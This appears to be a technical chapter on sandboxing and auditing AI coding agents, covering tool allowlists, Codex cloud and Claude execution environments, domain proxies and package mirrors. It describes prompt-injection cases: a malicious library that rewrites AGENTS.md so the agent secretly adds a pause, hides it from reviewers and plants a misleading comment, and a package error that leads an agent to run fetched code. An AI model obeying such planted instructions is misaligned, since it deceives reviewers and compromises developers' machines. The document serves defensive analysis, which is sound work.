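| What if the manager wants medians? | The agent writes another script | A developer writes a fifth tool and the auditors review it |

The third row can be worked out by counting. If each workbook has 12 columns, 4 of them numeric, there are 12 × 4 = 48 possible `total_by` calls per workbook and 96 for the two. An auditor can run all 96 and check the answers. Nobody can check every possible 5,000-character passage of free text, so even the second agent could write that sales rose when they fell.

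The tools are Python scripts, so the interpreter stays in the image, but the agent can no longer give it a script to run. This restriction depends on how the developers write the tools. If `total_by` also accepted a formula as text and passed it to Python for evaluation, the agent would have an interpreter again. The problem can be obvious from a tool's name. The example start-up record in the previous section includes `run_python`, so that agent belongs in the shell column despite its short list of tools.

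The main drawback of typed tools is lost flexibility, as the last row shows. Analysts ask for medians, then for a comparison with last year, then for a different date format, and each request may need another tool. Each tool the developers add gives the auditors more combinations to consider.

### The danger in an argument

Even a narrow tool can do harm. The call `total_by("payroll.xlsx", employee, salary)` has valid types and runs an approved script, but when the file has one row per employee, each total reveals one person's salary. A list that can only permit or forbid `total_by` as a whole cannot block this call without also blocking harmless ones.

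*Containing the Autonomous Operator* makes the same point about agents that manage Kubernetes, a system for running containers across many machines. It calls lists of permitted tools "necessary but insufficient". Its example is a tool that sets how many copies of a service run. Setting the number to ten may be the right response to heavy traffic, but the same tool can switch the service off by setting it to zero.

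The paper's design therefore puts a gateway between the agent and its tools. For each call, the gateway sends the agent's identity, the user, the tool and the arguments to a policy engine, a program that applies written rules. The sample policy lets the agent read logs in its assigned parts of the system and propose changes to approved code repositories. Restarting a production service requires a person's approval, and the policy forbids setting a service's number of copies to zero. Each approval is tied to a hash of the tool and its arguments, so the agent cannot reuse it for another action, and it also expires. The Kubernetes server independently enforces some of the same rules, which stops an agent that bypasses the gateway with a stolen credential.

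These rules are programs too, and they can be wrong. The sample policy has no rule for restarts in a development environment, so it blocks them by default, even though the paper's table of permissions lets agents make such changes there automatically. That mistake is overly cautious, but a rule can also be too loose. The ban on scaling a service to zero copies does not cover a cut from fifty copies to one, which could overload a busy service and do almost as much harm. In production, a person would see that request before it took effect.

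For the payroll, an operator could allow grouping only by department. The total for a department with one employee would still reveal that person's salary, so the tool would also need to withhold totals for very small groups. That check depends on the data as well as the arguments. The Kubernetes paper acknowledges that rules can exclude known bad arguments but cannot determine whether a permitted action is wise. It describes a design and reports no measurements of how many harmful calls the rules would stop.

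### Interpreters that check their scripts

Another approach is to keep the interpreter but extend the allowlist to its scripts. Microsoft's command shell, PowerShell, already does this. According to Microsoft's *How App Control works with PowerShell*, versions 7.3 and later check each script against the App Control policy, if Windows supports the check, and then run it normally, block it, or run it in a restricted mode. In that mode, a script cannot define classes, compile new .NET code or create objects outside an approved set. Commands that a user types always have the same restrictions while the policy is in force.

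Under App Control, even approved scripts lose some features. Developers of PowerShell modules, for example, have to name each function they export instead of using a wildcard. Auditors also have to read the logs carefully, because Windows may record a script as "blocked" when PowerShell ran it in restricted mode. App Control checks whether a script is approved, but the interpreter determines how to enforce the result.

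Linux lacked an equivalent for a long time. IMA checks a script that a user starts directly, as in `./report.py`, but not one that the user passes to the interpreter, as in `python report.py`. In a message archived by Openwall (2024), developers described control over scripts as necessary to close this gap. The kernel's creator, Linus Torvalds, merged the missing functions for Linux 6.14 on 23 January 2025 (*History log of /linux/Documentation/userspace-api/check_exec.rst*).

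The first function, `AT_EXECVE_CHECK`, lets an interpreter find out whether the kernel would allow a file to run, without running it. Two settings then tell the interpreter what to do. The Linux kernel documentation's *Executability check* describes the four combinations:

| `RESTRICT_FILE` | `DENY_INTERACTIVE` | What the interpreter should do |
|---|---|---|
| Off | Off | Run every script and every typed command |
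| On | Off | Run only scripts that pass the check, but accept typed commands |
| Off | On | Run every script, but refuse typed commands |
| On | On | Run only scripts that pass the check, and refuse typed commands |

Agents often run a few lines of Python by passing the code to the interpreter as an argument, and this counts as a typed command here. An operator who wants to exclude code the agent writes itself therefore needs both settings on.

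The spreadsheet container is nearly ready for this check. An interpreter that performed it would refuse any script the agent saved in the container's `noexec` folders. The scripts in `/opt/agent` could still run if the operator marked them as executable. The check should also cover every library file that Python loads. Many of those aren't marked as executable, so the operator would have to mark files throughout pandas and numpy when building the image.

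The larger obstacle is that the kernel cannot force an interpreter to make the check. The forum user who asked for it in Python found no progress elsewhere except an open request for Perl. A respondent, apparently from the Python team, doubted that the standard version would include it, because the team lacked the staff to promise complete protection, and suggested a custom build instead. A custom build is feasible, since the secure operating system CLIP OS used modified interpreters with an earlier form of the check for more than a decade, according to the kernel's log.

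Even a modified interpreter leaves a small gap between checking a script and running it, during which someone could alter the script. An August 2025 proposal, *Add O_DENY_WRITE (complement AT_EXECVE_CHECK)*, would let interpreters block changes during that time. The gap matters less in the spreadsheet container, where the agent cannot write to the approved scripts. According to the kernel's log, the settings only make sense if the process that starts the interpreter is trustworthy, since a malicious one could run its own code instead. The operator therefore still has to audit the harness.

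With both settings on, the spreadsheet agent could run only the scripts the auditors had read, much like the agent with four typed tools. A coding agent could hardly work under that rule, because to fix a failing test it has to change the code and run the changed version, which no auditor has approved.

### Letting the agent write code

Operators of coding agents mostly have to accept programs that the agent writes itself and audit what those programs can affect. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* assumes that such code is hostile. Its sandboxes hold no credentials and usually have no network connection, and the sample configuration limits each one to one processor core, 1 GiB of memory and 512 MiB of temporary storage. A monitoring program in the kernel also kills any process that tries to open the folder where Kubernetes normally keeps credentials. That folder should not exist in the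 sandbox, so an attempt to read it suggests an attack.

Before the agent starts, an auditor can test such limits by running a script that tries to open a connection, write to a protected folder and request more memory than allowed. All three attempts should fail. While the agent works, the harness can save every command and script so that investigators can later read the code that ran. The operator still has to trust the isolation software.

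None of these tests shows that the agent's work is correct. A script that silently drops every sale with no region would stay within all the limits and still produce a wrong total. Someone has to read the script or repeat the calculation, and an agent can write scripts faster than people can review them.

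## OpenAI's Codex cloud, which installs with network access and works without it

Codex is OpenAI's coding agent. In its cloud version, released in May 2025, the agent works in a container on OpenAI's servers and a developer reviews the changes afterwards. Like any coding agent, it has to run code that no auditor has read, so OpenAI limits what that code can reach. The container has no internet access while the agent works, unless the customer switches it on, but it downloads the project's packages over an open connection before the agent starts.

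The process for the spreadsheet image was stricter because reviewers read the packages before the operator installed them offline. Codex cloud does not require anyone to read the packages between the download and the agent's first command.

### One task, step by step

Suppose a developer asks Codex to fix a failing test in an online shop's code. According to OpenAI's *Cloud environments*, Codex first creates a container and checks out the repository at the branch or commit the developer selected. It then runs a setup script, which has full internet access, to install the shop's packages. Next, it applies the agent's network setting, which blocks internet access by default. The agent edits files and runs tests in a loop, then shows its answer with a diff, a line-by-line record of its changes. The developer can turn the diff into a pull request, a proposed change that colleagues review before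 it enters the main code.

By default, setup scripts in Codex cloud can use the internet and the agent cannot. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* calls this a two-phase runtime model, and the Chinese edition of OpenAI's network guide, *智能体互联网访问*, gives the same defaults.

Codex can install dependencies itself for projects that use common package managers, such as npm or pip. Other projects need a custom setup script. Some users did not know that network access ends after setup until their agent tried to use it. In the forum thread *Codex cloud agent unable to install pnpm dependencies*, an agent reported that a network problem had stopped it from installing packages and that it would try the tests anyway. Another user's solution was to put the install command in the setup script.

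A customer can also give the agent access to the whole network or only to chosen addresses, and OpenAI offers a preset list of common package sites. OpenAI's *Introducing upgrades to Codex* (2025) points out that the agent can then run `pip install` whenever it needs something while it works. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* warns that the agent may download malware or follow instructions hidden in text it reads. Its example is a bug report containing a command that sends the project's latest commit message to a stranger's server.

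### Secrets that disappear before the agent starts

Setup may need a password or an access key, for example to download from a company's private package registry. OpenAI stores these secrets with an extra layer of encryption, makes them available only during setup, and removes them before the agent phase. Ordinary environment variables, which are named values that programs can read, remain for the whole task, so the agent can read a key that someone saves as one by mistake.

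Removing the secrets before the agent starts protects them from the agent and anyone who tricks it, but not from the packages installed during setup. Many package managers let a package run its own code during installation, when it would have access to both the secrets and the network. A malicious package could therefore send a registry key to its author.

A secret can also outlast the setup phase if the setup script copies it into a file. OpenAI suggests using the shell's start-up file, `~/.bashrc`, for variables that should persist into the agent phase. If a script saved a registry key there, the agent would have access to the copy even after the original variable was deleted. For a related service that hosts sandboxes for other agents, OpenAI recommends vault credentials, which keep the real values outside the sandbox.

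### The universal image and the 12-hour cache

Each container starts from an image called `universal`, which includes common programming languages and tools. Customers can choose versions of Python, Node.js and other language runtimes under a setting called "Set package versions". Despite its name, the setting does not apply to the packages a project installs, so a shop that fixes its Node.js version can still receive a new release of its payment library.

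OpenAI publishes a reference Dockerfile and a downloadable copy of the image so that developers can test their setup locally. The copy is "not an identical environment", according to the project's description, reproduced in Ecosyste.ms' *codex-universal* (2025). An auditor can learn a lot from the copy, but its digest would not identify the software in the cloud. The sample download command also uses the moving label `latest` instead of a digest.

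To avoid reinstalling everything for each task, Codex saves the container after setup and reuses it for up to 12 hours. OpenAI says this caching cut the median completion time of new tasks and follow-ups by 90%. To fill the cache, Codex checks out the repository's default branch and runs the setup script. When a later task resumes the saved container, Codex switches to that task's branch and runs an optional maintenance script, which can update the packages. In the lifecycle diagram in *Codex Cloud Environment Configuration* (Vaughan, 2026), both scripts run before network access is restricted, so the maintenance script can also download new software.

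Because of this order, the agent can test against the wrong library version even when the lockfile is correct. Suppose the shop's default branch locks version 4.1 of the payment library, and a developer's branch locks 4.2. The cached container holds 4.1, so without a maintenance script, the agent tests the developer's branch against the old version. A maintenance script that repeats the locked installation fixes the problem.

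Codex discards the cache automatically when someone changes either script, an environment variable or a secret, but not when a package is found to be malicious. If setup installed a malicious release at 9 a.m. and its publisher withdrew it at 10 a.m., new tasks could keep running it until 9 p.m. unless someone selected "Reset cache". On Business and Enterprise plans, everyone with access to the environment shares its cache, so colleagues' tasks would run the malicious release too.

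### Two runs on either side of a release

A dated example shows how the same commit can lead to different software. Suppose a project's tests call the command-line version of Codex, and its setup script therefore contains this line:

```
npm install -g @openai/codex
```

The line doesn't specify a version, so npm installs the current one. According to Releasebot's *Codex Updates & Release Notes* (2026), a page that collects software announcements, OpenAI released version 0.169.0 on 13 November 2026 and version 0.170.0 on 18 November. A developer who started tasks on 17 and 19 November with the same commit and script would have received 0.169.0 in the first task and 0.170.0 in the second.

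One of the security fixes in 0.170.0 corrected a fault in which child threads, pieces of work started from another conversation, lost their sandbox restrictions. The second task therefore had better software, but an auditor who had examined only the first container would not have seen the newer version. On the day of the release, two tasks a few minutes apart could have run different versions if someone had reset the cache between them.

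OpenAI's sample setup script contains a similar line, `pip install pyright`, which installs a tool that checks Python code for type errors. The next two commands, `poetry install` and `pnpm install`, can use a lockfile if the repository has one. An extra tool in the setup script may therefore change from one cache to the next, even in a project that locks all its own packages. GitHub's *About customizing Copilot cloud agent's development environment* gives a sample configuration that uses `npm ci`, which installs exactly what the lockfile lists and stops if the lockfile is missing or doesn't match the project's list of requirements.

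The table shows what holds each part of a Codex task in place.

| Part | What fixes it | When it can still change |
|---|---|---|
| Source code | A commit identifier | When the task names a branch instead |
| Python, Node.js and other runtimes | The version setting | When someone edits the setting |
| Rest of the universal image | OpenAI's choice of image | When OpenAI updates it |
| Project packages | A lockfile that the install command obeys | At setup or maintenance, if there is none |
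| Extra tools in the setup script | A version named in the script | At each new setup, if the script names none |
| Harness and model | OpenAI | When OpenAI updates them |

Installation therefore ends and work begins at the start of a task, but an audit may have taken place months earlier or not at all. Turning the network off prevents the agent from adding downloaded program files to the container during that task. Guaranteeing a fixed stack also requires every program file in the container at the start of each task to have an approved hash, and Codex does not prompt the customer for a list of approved hashes.

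OpenAI reworked Codex cloud in September 2026, and the boundary between setup and work may now be closer to an audit. According to CodeReport Global's *OpenAI Codex Cloud* (2026), Codex now inspects the project and prepares an environment with its tools and packages. A person reviews the setup report and files and then publishes the environment, and every new task starts in a separate workspace based on it. An auditor could examine the environment just before it is published.

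That examination would be worth more if publishing saves the installed files, because later tasks would then run what the reviewer saw. If publishing saves only the install commands, each task may download something new. Punto Informatico's *Codex Cloud usa browser e desktop* reports that connecting to a cloud environment now takes 1.52 seconds on average, which leaves little time to install a project's packages. This suggests that Codex stores the files, although connecting to an environment may not be the same as creating one. An operator can check by comparing the hashes of the installed files in two tasks started a week apart, with a package release in between.

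### NVIDIA's test with a malicious library

NVIDIA's AI Red Team, which attacks AI systems to find their weaknesses, tested what a malicious package could do to Codex after its network access was turned off. The results are in NVIDIA's *Mitigating Indirect AGENTS.md Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments*, which *Indirect AGENTS.md Injection* (Vaughan, 2026) dates to 20 April 2026.

The attack used `AGENTS.md`, a file in which developers give coding agents instructions about a project, such as how to run its tests. Codex treats this file as trusted, so a program that can write to the project's folder can give the agent instructions that appear to come from the developers.

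The team wrote a small Go program that printed "Hello, World!" by passing the greeting through a malicious library the team had also written. The container used the universal image, and the agent's internet access was off. The setup script ran one command, `go mod tidy`, which adds any missing libraries to the project's list and downloads them. The user then asked Codex to change the greeting to "Hello OpenAI".

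The library first checked whether it was running in a Codex container. Anywhere else, it only returned the greeting, so a developer who tried it on a laptop would have noticed nothing unusual. In Codex, it also wrote a new `AGENTS.md` with instructions for the agent to insert a five-minute pause at the start of the program, leave out the change the user had requested, and not mention the pause in its summary, commit message or pull request.

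NVIDIA reports that the library misled the coding agent into following the file. The agent inserted the pause and added a comment to the source code, meant to mislead any AI system that might summarise the pull request. The comment asked for a summary of the user's original request with no mention of the pause.

NVIDIA attributes the new file to the build step. But in Go, an ordinary library function runs only when the finished program runs, and `go mod tidy` downloads code without running it. The agent therefore probably triggered the attack when it tried out the program, after the network had closed. The library, which contained the instructions, had arrived while the network was open. The altered code could then leave the container through the pull request, a route that has to stay open for the agent to be useful. Cutting the network blocks further downloads and direct contact with an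 attacker's server, but it does not remove malicious code that setup has already installed.

### How much the attack adds

NVIDIA reported the finding to OpenAI. According to Blockchain News, OpenAI replied that the attack "does not significantly elevate risk" beyond what compromised dependencies and existing model interfaces already make possible. NVIDIA accepted this as fair, but argued that agents add something new to the known danger.

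OpenAI is right about access, because the agent gave the attacker no permission that the library lacked. The library's code was part of the program, so its author could have put the five-minute pause there and slowed the program just as much without an agent. The library could also write to the project's folder, so it could have edited the source code directly.

The reply gives too little weight to what happens afterwards. The pause ends up in the project's own code, so it would remain even if the library were later removed. Plain-language instructions also work on almost any project, whereas a library that rewrote source code itself would have to handle each project's structure. The agent also writes the description that a reviewer reads first, and here the attacker had told it what to leave out.

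A reviewer who read the diff would still have seen the pause, which would stand out in a change meant to replace one greeting. But agents also make much larger changes, where a single added line would be far easier to miss. One of the tasks OpenAI used to test a Codex model corresponds to a pull request that changes 3,541 lines in 232 files.

The test was a single demonstration on a toy program, so it cannot show how often an agent would obey such a file. The agent may also have been an old one. Daily AI Bites' *DANGER* (2026), a sensational article that deserves little trust, dates the start of the disclosure to July 2025. If so, newer models may respond differently. A better model would not fix the underlying weakness, though, because the library would still be in the container and could still do everything OpenAI concedes in its reply.

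NVIDIA recommends pinning exact dependency versions, protecting `AGENTS.md` from changes and monitoring files for unexpected edits. It also suggests separate security agents and two NVIDIA tools that test for or filter malicious instructions. Pinning helps when an attacker takes over a library that used to be safe, because the project keeps the old version. It would not have helped here unless someone had read the library first, because the team wrote the library to be malicious.

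Protecting the instruction file addresses this attack more directly. In the version of Codex that runs on a user's own computer, the default sandbox lets the agent write to the project's folder but keeps `.git`, `.agents` and `.codex` within it read-only. OpenAI does not list `AGENTS.md` among the protected paths. An operator could have the harness take instructions only from the committed version of the file, or compare the file with that version after each task and reject the work if they differ. Git would list a newly created `AGENTS.md` as untracked, but it normally wouldn't show that a program had altered an installed package, because most projects configure Git to ignore package folders.

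### What an operator would add

To make a Codex environment auditable, an operator would begin with the setup script. Every tool in it needs an exact version, and every install command has to obey a lockfile with hashes. The script can then compare the installed files with a list that the auditors approved. For the online shop, the main part might look like this:

```
set -euo pipefail
npm ci --ignore-scripts
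find node_modules -type f -exec sha256sum {} + | LC_ALL=C sort > /tmp/now.txt
diff audit/node_modules.sha256 /tmp/now.txt
```

The first line makes the script stop at any error. The second installs the locked packages without running their installation code, so a malicious package can't read the setup secrets or tamper with the comparison. Some packages don't work unless their installation code runs, and the auditors would have to review and permit those individually. The third line lists the hash of every installed file, and the fourth causes an error if the list differs from the approved one. The maintenance script should contain the same four lines, since it can change the packages after setup has passed the check.

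The error is useful only if it prevents the agent from starting. OpenAI says a failed setup command does so in its separate service for hosted sandboxes, but Codex cloud may behave differently. The forum post *Codex cloud* describes an agent that could not build a project because setup had failed and the packages were missing, which suggests that the agent had started anyway. An operator should therefore test this by putting a wrong hash in the approved list and checking whether the task stops.

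The same user estimated that network problems broke setup about 30% of the time, and wished for local package mirrors or custom Docker images. Both would also help an auditor. If a mirror held only reviewed packages, a mistake in the setup script could not easily install anything else, although the script would still have full internet access and could bypass the mirror. The reworked Codex cloud can also reach private systems through Tailscale, a service that connects machines in a closed network, and an operator might be able to place the mirror there. However, each private system the agent can reach adds to the stack that needs an audit.

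A custom image with a recorded digest would go further. Cursor, a competing coding agent, lets customers describe their environment in a Dockerfile. According to its *Cloud Environment Setup*, Cursor runs the install script while creating a stored build, before any agent starts. An auditor could examine that build once, provided later tasks use it unchanged.

Each task would also need a start-up record like the one for the spreadsheet agent, plus the commit, the hashes of both scripts and the list of installed files. An investigator could then tell which packages were present when the agent made a particular change.

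The remaining gaps are the universal image, the harness and the model, all of which OpenAI controls. To freeze the first two, an operator can run the agent's commands in their own environment, which OpenAI supports for some of its agents. OpenAI's sample instructions install the Codex program with `npm install -g @openai/codex@alpha`. The `alpha` label moves to each new test release, so the operator would have to replace it with an exact version. The model would still run on OpenAI's servers. When OpenAI released GPT-5-Codex to developers in September 2025, it announced that it would regularly update the model behind that name.

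## Claude's execution containers and the addresses an agent may contact

Codex cloud cuts off network access after installation, before the agent starts work, but a customer can instead let the agent reach a chosen list of addresses. Anthropic offers a similar option for Claude, along with stricter and looser ones. The same skill, or small add-on, can run in a container with no network access, on a machine limited to a list of permitted domains, or on a laptop with full internet access. An auditor can make different claims about the skill in each setting.

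### One skill in four environments

A company might write a skill called `invoice-check` for its accountants. The skill's script reads PDF invoices with the Python package pdfplumber, reads their barcodes with a less common package, and fetches the day's exchange rates from a bank's website.

Developers who build Claude into their software through Anthropic's API can have it run code in a container on Anthropic's servers. According to Anthropic's *Code execution tool*, this container has no internet access, so only pre-installed libraries are available. Anthropic's list of these includes pdfplumber but not the barcode package, so the developers would have to put the barcode code into the skill. They would also have to upload the exchange rates as a file, because the script can't reach the bank.

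Anthropic's *Create and edit files with Claude* describes four levels of network access that an organisation can choose from for the Claude web, desktop and phone apps: no network, package managers only, package managers plus named domains, or every domain except those on a legal blocklist. With package managers only, Claude can install the barcode package from PyPI during a conversation but cannot reach the bank's site.

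When Claude Code runs on a user's own computer, a skill has the same network access as any other program there, according to Anthropic's *Agent Skills*. All three parts of the script can therefore work. Claude Code can also run on a virtual machine that Anthropic hosts, where a new environment starts with a long list of permitted domains. The list includes PyPI, so Claude can install the barcode package, but someone has to add the bank's domain.

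| Environment | Barcode package | Exchange rates | What an auditor can assert |
|---|---|---|---|
| API container | Unavailable | Blocked | The container downloads nothing while Claude works |
| Claude apps, network off | Unavailable | Blocked | The same, apart from data that connected tools bring in |
| Claude apps, package managers only | Claude can install it | Blocked | Downloads come from a short list of domains |
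| Claude Code, hosted, default settings | Claude can install it | Blocked | Downloads come from a long list of domains or a few separate routes |
| Claude Code, user's computer | Claude can install it | Available | Only what the user's own controls enforce |

These claims come from Anthropic's documentation. An operator can test some of them by asking Claude to download a harmless file and checking that the attempt fails.

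### Gaps in the stricter environments

The API container comes closest to a sealed image, but the customer doesn't control it. Anthropic names the pre-installed libraries without giving their versions or a digest, so the software could change between two jobs even if the customer's request stays the same. An operator can have Claude run `pip freeze` at the start of each job to list the installed Python packages and their versions, then compare the results.

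Each request gets a new container unless the developer sends back the identifier of an earlier one, which works for up to 30 days. A reused container keeps the files from earlier requests, which may include a script that Claude wrote three weeks ago. Every audited job therefore needs a new container to start from a known state.

Code can also enter the container without a network. Anthropic supports uploading Python files, and a skill brings its own scripts. Claude normally runs these scripts without reading their code, so it sees only the output and can't notice a suspicious line. A person has to review every copy of a script beforehand, because custom skills don't sync between the API, the apps and Claude Code. In the apps, each member uploads a separate copy that administrators can't manage centrally, so ten accountants could be using ten different versions of `invoice-check`.

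An API request can also include tools such as web search and web fetch, which bring outside text to the model even though the container is offline. The current versions of these two tools filter their results inside the container. An auditor who reads only the container's network setting would miss this, so they also have to review the request's full list of tools.

For the apps, the auditor needs to check the organisation's actual setting, because Anthropic's help page gives two different defaults for Team plans. Network access is off in one passage and limited to package managers in another. Anthropic also claims that switching off network access eliminates the risk of data leaving the sandbox, but adds that MCP connections keep working whatever the setting. The claim can therefore hold only for users without MCP connections.

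On a user's own computer, the main control is an optional sandbox for shell commands. The user defines which files and domains the commands may access, and the operating system enforces these limits on each command and every program it starts, according to Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool*. When a command requests a new domain, Claude Code prompts the user for permission, so the list of allowed domains can grow while the agent works. Claude Code's built-in tools for reading and editing files run outside this sandbox. They follow separate permission rules, according to a University of Vermont guide, so blocking a file under one set of rules doesn't necessarily block it under the other.

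### The hosted version of Claude Code

Anthropic offers three network levels for its hosted machines: None, Limited and Full. The default is Limited with the "Allow package managers" box ticked, which permits the whole default list. Unlike in Codex, the chosen level applies to both the setup script and the agent. If an operator allows access to PyPI so that the setup script can install packages, Claude can also install more packages from PyPI during the session.

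An operator could try to imitate Codex by switching network access to None after setup. Running sessions adopt the new setting within about a minute and keep the packages they already have. New sessions normally start from a snapshot of the file system that Anthropic saves after setup, but changing the allowed hosts makes the setup script run again, and its installations would fail with access set to None.

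The snapshot expires after about seven days, even if nobody changes anything. The next setup may then install newer versions, unless the script installs the versions pinned in a lockfile. Anthropic doesn't yet let customers replace the base image, but they can run a container from their own image on the hosted machine.

Some traffic bypasses the domain list at every access level. GitHub operations use a separate proxy, and MCP connectors go through Anthropic's servers. If the operator stores a secret key for a particular host, sessions can usually reach that host even when the level is None. Claude Code also keeps a connection to Anthropic's API, and Anthropic warns that this may let data leave the machine.

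The rules behind these settings can change too. In July 2026, according to Anthropic's *Configure cloud environments*, the GitHub proxy let the agent push code only to the session's current working branch. By November, the proxy no longer limited which branches a push could update, and Anthropic referred customers to GitHub's own branch protection. The July documentation also listed a record of requested host names as a feature of the general network proxy, but the November version does not. An auditor who relied on either feature in July would have needed to check again.

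### How a proxy applies a list of domains

A container restricted to certain domains should have no direct route to the internet. Its programs send their requests to a proxy, a relay program that runs outside the container, where the agent can't edit the rules. When Claude installs the barcode package, the download goes through these steps:

1. pip asks the proxy for a connection to `files.pythonhosted.org`, the server that holds PyPI's files.
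2. The proxy compares this name with its list. In Anthropic's lists, an entry that begins with `*.` matches every subdomain, so `*.gcr.io` covers any name that ends in `.gcr.io`.
3. If an entry matches, the proxy opens the connection and passes data in both directions. Otherwise it refuses.

pip and the server encrypt what they send each other. A proxy that only relays the data can see the server's name, the time and the amount of traffic, but not which package pip requested or whether a program uploaded a file. Its log could show that the agent contacted PyPI at 10:14 and received two megabytes. It could not show whether those two megabytes were the barcode package or something else. Where many websites share one delivery network, the encrypted request may even name a different site from the one the proxy approved.

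To inspect more of the traffic, the proxy has to decrypt it. The proxy presents its own certificate, which the operator has configured the container to trust, reads the request, and encrypts it again for the real server. It can then apply rules to full addresses and contents. But decryption also exposes every password and key in the traffic to the proxy, and programs that accept only the real server's certificate stop working.

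A limit on HTTP methods is one rule that needs this access. The method is the part of a web request that specifies its purpose. For example, GET asks for a page or file, and POST sends data. OpenAI lets Codex cloud customers restrict the agent to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, which all request information. The version of Codex for a user's own computer has a similar limited mode. *Codex CLI Network Proxy* (Vaughan, 2026) explains that this mode disables SOCKS5, a general protocol for relaying connections, because the proxy can't read encrypted traffic inside it to check whether a request only reads data.

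Blocking POST prevents ordinary uploads, but a program can still put data into the address of a GET request, and the receiving server can record it. Blocking POST also prevents some legitimate work, such as cloning a Git repository over HTTPS, which normally requires POST. pip can still download packages with GET alone.

Rules can also depend on which program makes the request. In NVIDIA's *Default Policy Reference*, which covers a sandbox for agents, each rule pairs a set of destinations with a set of programs. The proxy uses the operating system to identify the program that opened a connection, and refuses the connection unless a rule includes both the program and the destination. It decrypts traffic to Anthropic's API but not traffic to the error-reporting service Sentry. These rules could let Claude Code reach its model while denying other programs access to the same address. They can't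 be used to treat Python scripts differently, because the operating system reports each script as the Python interpreter.

### The preset lists

OpenAI offers a preset list of 71 domains called "Common dependencies". It covers package registries, code hosts, Linux distributions and large software companies. Customers can add to it or start from an empty list. OpenAI updates the preset as development tools change, so an auditor should save a dated copy.

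OpenAI's entries probably include subdomains. The preset lists `npmjs.org`, but npm normally downloads packages from `registry.npmjs.org`, so the preset would be of little use to JavaScript projects if it matched only exact names. If subdomains are included, the `azure.com` entry would also let an agent contact strangers' servers, because Microsoft gives customers who rent its virtual machines names that end in `cloudapp.azure.com`. The `google.com` entry would include Google Forms, where anyone can create an online form.

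Anthropic's list for the Claude apps has 16 names, nearly all of them for package downloads. The default list for hosted Claude Code had about 200 entries in July 2026, including `*.amazonaws.com` and `*.googleapis.com`, which cover storage that anyone can rent from Amazon and Google. By November, it also included `*.r2.cloudflarestorage.com`, a similar service from Cloudflare.

Such broad entries are useful because many projects keep large files in rented storage, and an installation fails if any of its downloads is blocked. An operator with a single well-understood project can start with an empty list, run the installation, and add only the names the proxy refused. The `invoice-check` skill would probably need only PyPI's two main addresses and the bank's.

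### Permitted domains and unapproved software

An agent may download software from a permitted domain, but the domain's owner has usually not examined what other people upload there. Anyone with an account can publish a package on PyPI or npm, including under a name that a language model has made up. In July 2026, the default list of permitted domains for hosted Claude Code also included `test.pypi.org`, a separate registry where developers practise publishing. The proxy allows both a reviewed package and a malicious one uploaded an hour ago, because both come from a permitted address.

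The content at an address can also change. If the address of an installation script on GitHub contains the branch name `main`, the server returns whatever is on that branch at the time. The agent could therefore run a different script from the harmless one an auditor read the day before. Replacing `main` with a commit identifier keeps the script's contents from changing, but the script may still download the latest version of something else. Anthropic warns that even trustworthy skills can become unsafe if the outside sources they depend on change.

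Access to code on GitHub is also difficult to block. In hosted Claude Code, the GitHub proxy refuses to download a full archive of any repository that the user hasn't attached to the session, even a public one. But the default domain list includes `raw.githubusercontent.com`, so an agent can still download files from any public repository one at a time.

An agent can also leak data through permitted sites. A domain list would stop the attack in OpenAI's example of a malicious bug report, because the attacker's server is not on the list. But an attacker who rented storage under `*.amazonaws.com` could receive the same data at a permitted address. A short list reduces this risk but does not remove it. The 16 domain names allowed for the Claude apps include Anthropic's API, which accepts file uploads from customers. Unless Anthropic checks whose account a request uses, an agent could in principle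 upload a file to an attacker's account.

Researchers at Mozilla's Zero Day Investigative Network (0DIN) demonstrated in 2026 that inspecting a project may reveal little about the code that eventually runs. According to Help Net Security's *Mozilla warns of indirect prompt injection risk in AI coding agents*, they prepared a project with ordinary-looking setup instructions and no harmful code. One of its packages failed on first use and displayed an instruction for the user to run another command. A coding agent that followed the instruction fetched code from a source the researchers controlled and ran it immediately, which gave them control of the developer's machine with the developer's permissions.

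An auditor could have read every file in that project and found nothing worse than a command that fetches text and runs it. An attacker could also supply harmless text during the audit and replace it afterwards. Checking program files by hash would not have helped, because the harmful commands arrived as text and were run by the shell, an approved interpreter.

The researchers used their own source, so a strict domain list would probably have blocked the fetch if the agent had no other way to query the internet. The list would not have blocked the same text on a permitted code host. The demonstration was a proof of concept, and Help Net Security reports no success rate, so it is unclear how often agents would run the command.

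0DIN recommends that coding agents show what a command will execute, including anything it fetches, not just the text of the command. Auditors can apply the same idea earlier by searching a project's scripts for commands that download code and immediately run it. They can then save a copy of that code, review it, and change the script to use the copy.

### Approved mirrors and relays

Because anyone can publish on a public registry, some operators let their agents download packages only from a server inside the organisation. An approved mirror contains only packages that reviewers have copied into it, and a request for anything else fails. A relay, or pull-through cache, can start empty. When an agent requests a package, the relay fetches it from the public registry, keeps a copy and passes it on.

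A mirror and a relay can have the same internal address and work with the same pip commands, so the agent's settings may not show which one it uses. An auditor can find out by requesting a harmless public package that nobody has approved. The mirror will return an error, while a relay without further restrictions will deliver the package.

A relay still has advantages over direct access. It can keep a package available after the publisher deletes it. Unlike a proxy that only forwards encrypted traffic, it can also log the exact package and version each agent requested. Some products can reject very new releases or known malicious ones. But a relay may keep supplying a malicious release from its own copy after the public registry has removed it.

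An approved mirror is safer but takes more work. For `invoice-check`, reviewers would have to approve pdfplumber, the barcode package and everything the two depend on, and repeat the process for each security update. That is manageable for one skill with a stable set of packages. For a coding agent that works on dozens of projects, the delays could lead developers to look for ways around the mirror.

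A relay combined with a lockfile of reviewed hashes offers some of the same protection with less effort. But the lockfile protects only installations that use it, and an agent that can run pip freely can install a package by name instead.

pip's settings also matter. The option `--index-url` makes pip use the mirror in place of PyPI, while `--extra-index-url` adds the mirror to PyPI. With the second option, pip may choose a higher version from PyPI over the one that reviewers approved. The agent could also name PyPI in its own command, so the operator has to block PyPI in the network rules as well.

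The package server is also software that an agent can reach, and it may have flaws. In July 2026, OpenAI (2026) found that agents in an internal test had reached the internet through the package service meant to replace direct access. An audit therefore has to include the package server and its security updates. A relay needs an outgoing internet connection, but an approved mirror doesn't if reviewers bring the packages in by another route.

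To use an approved mirror with hosted Claude Code, the operator unticks "Allow package managers" and adds the mirror's address to the permitted domains. The mirror must then accept connections from Anthropic's network, but the operator can still block the mirror's outgoing connections. Organisations that don't want to expose the mirror can run Claude Code's cloud sessions on their own machines and restrict network access on those machines.

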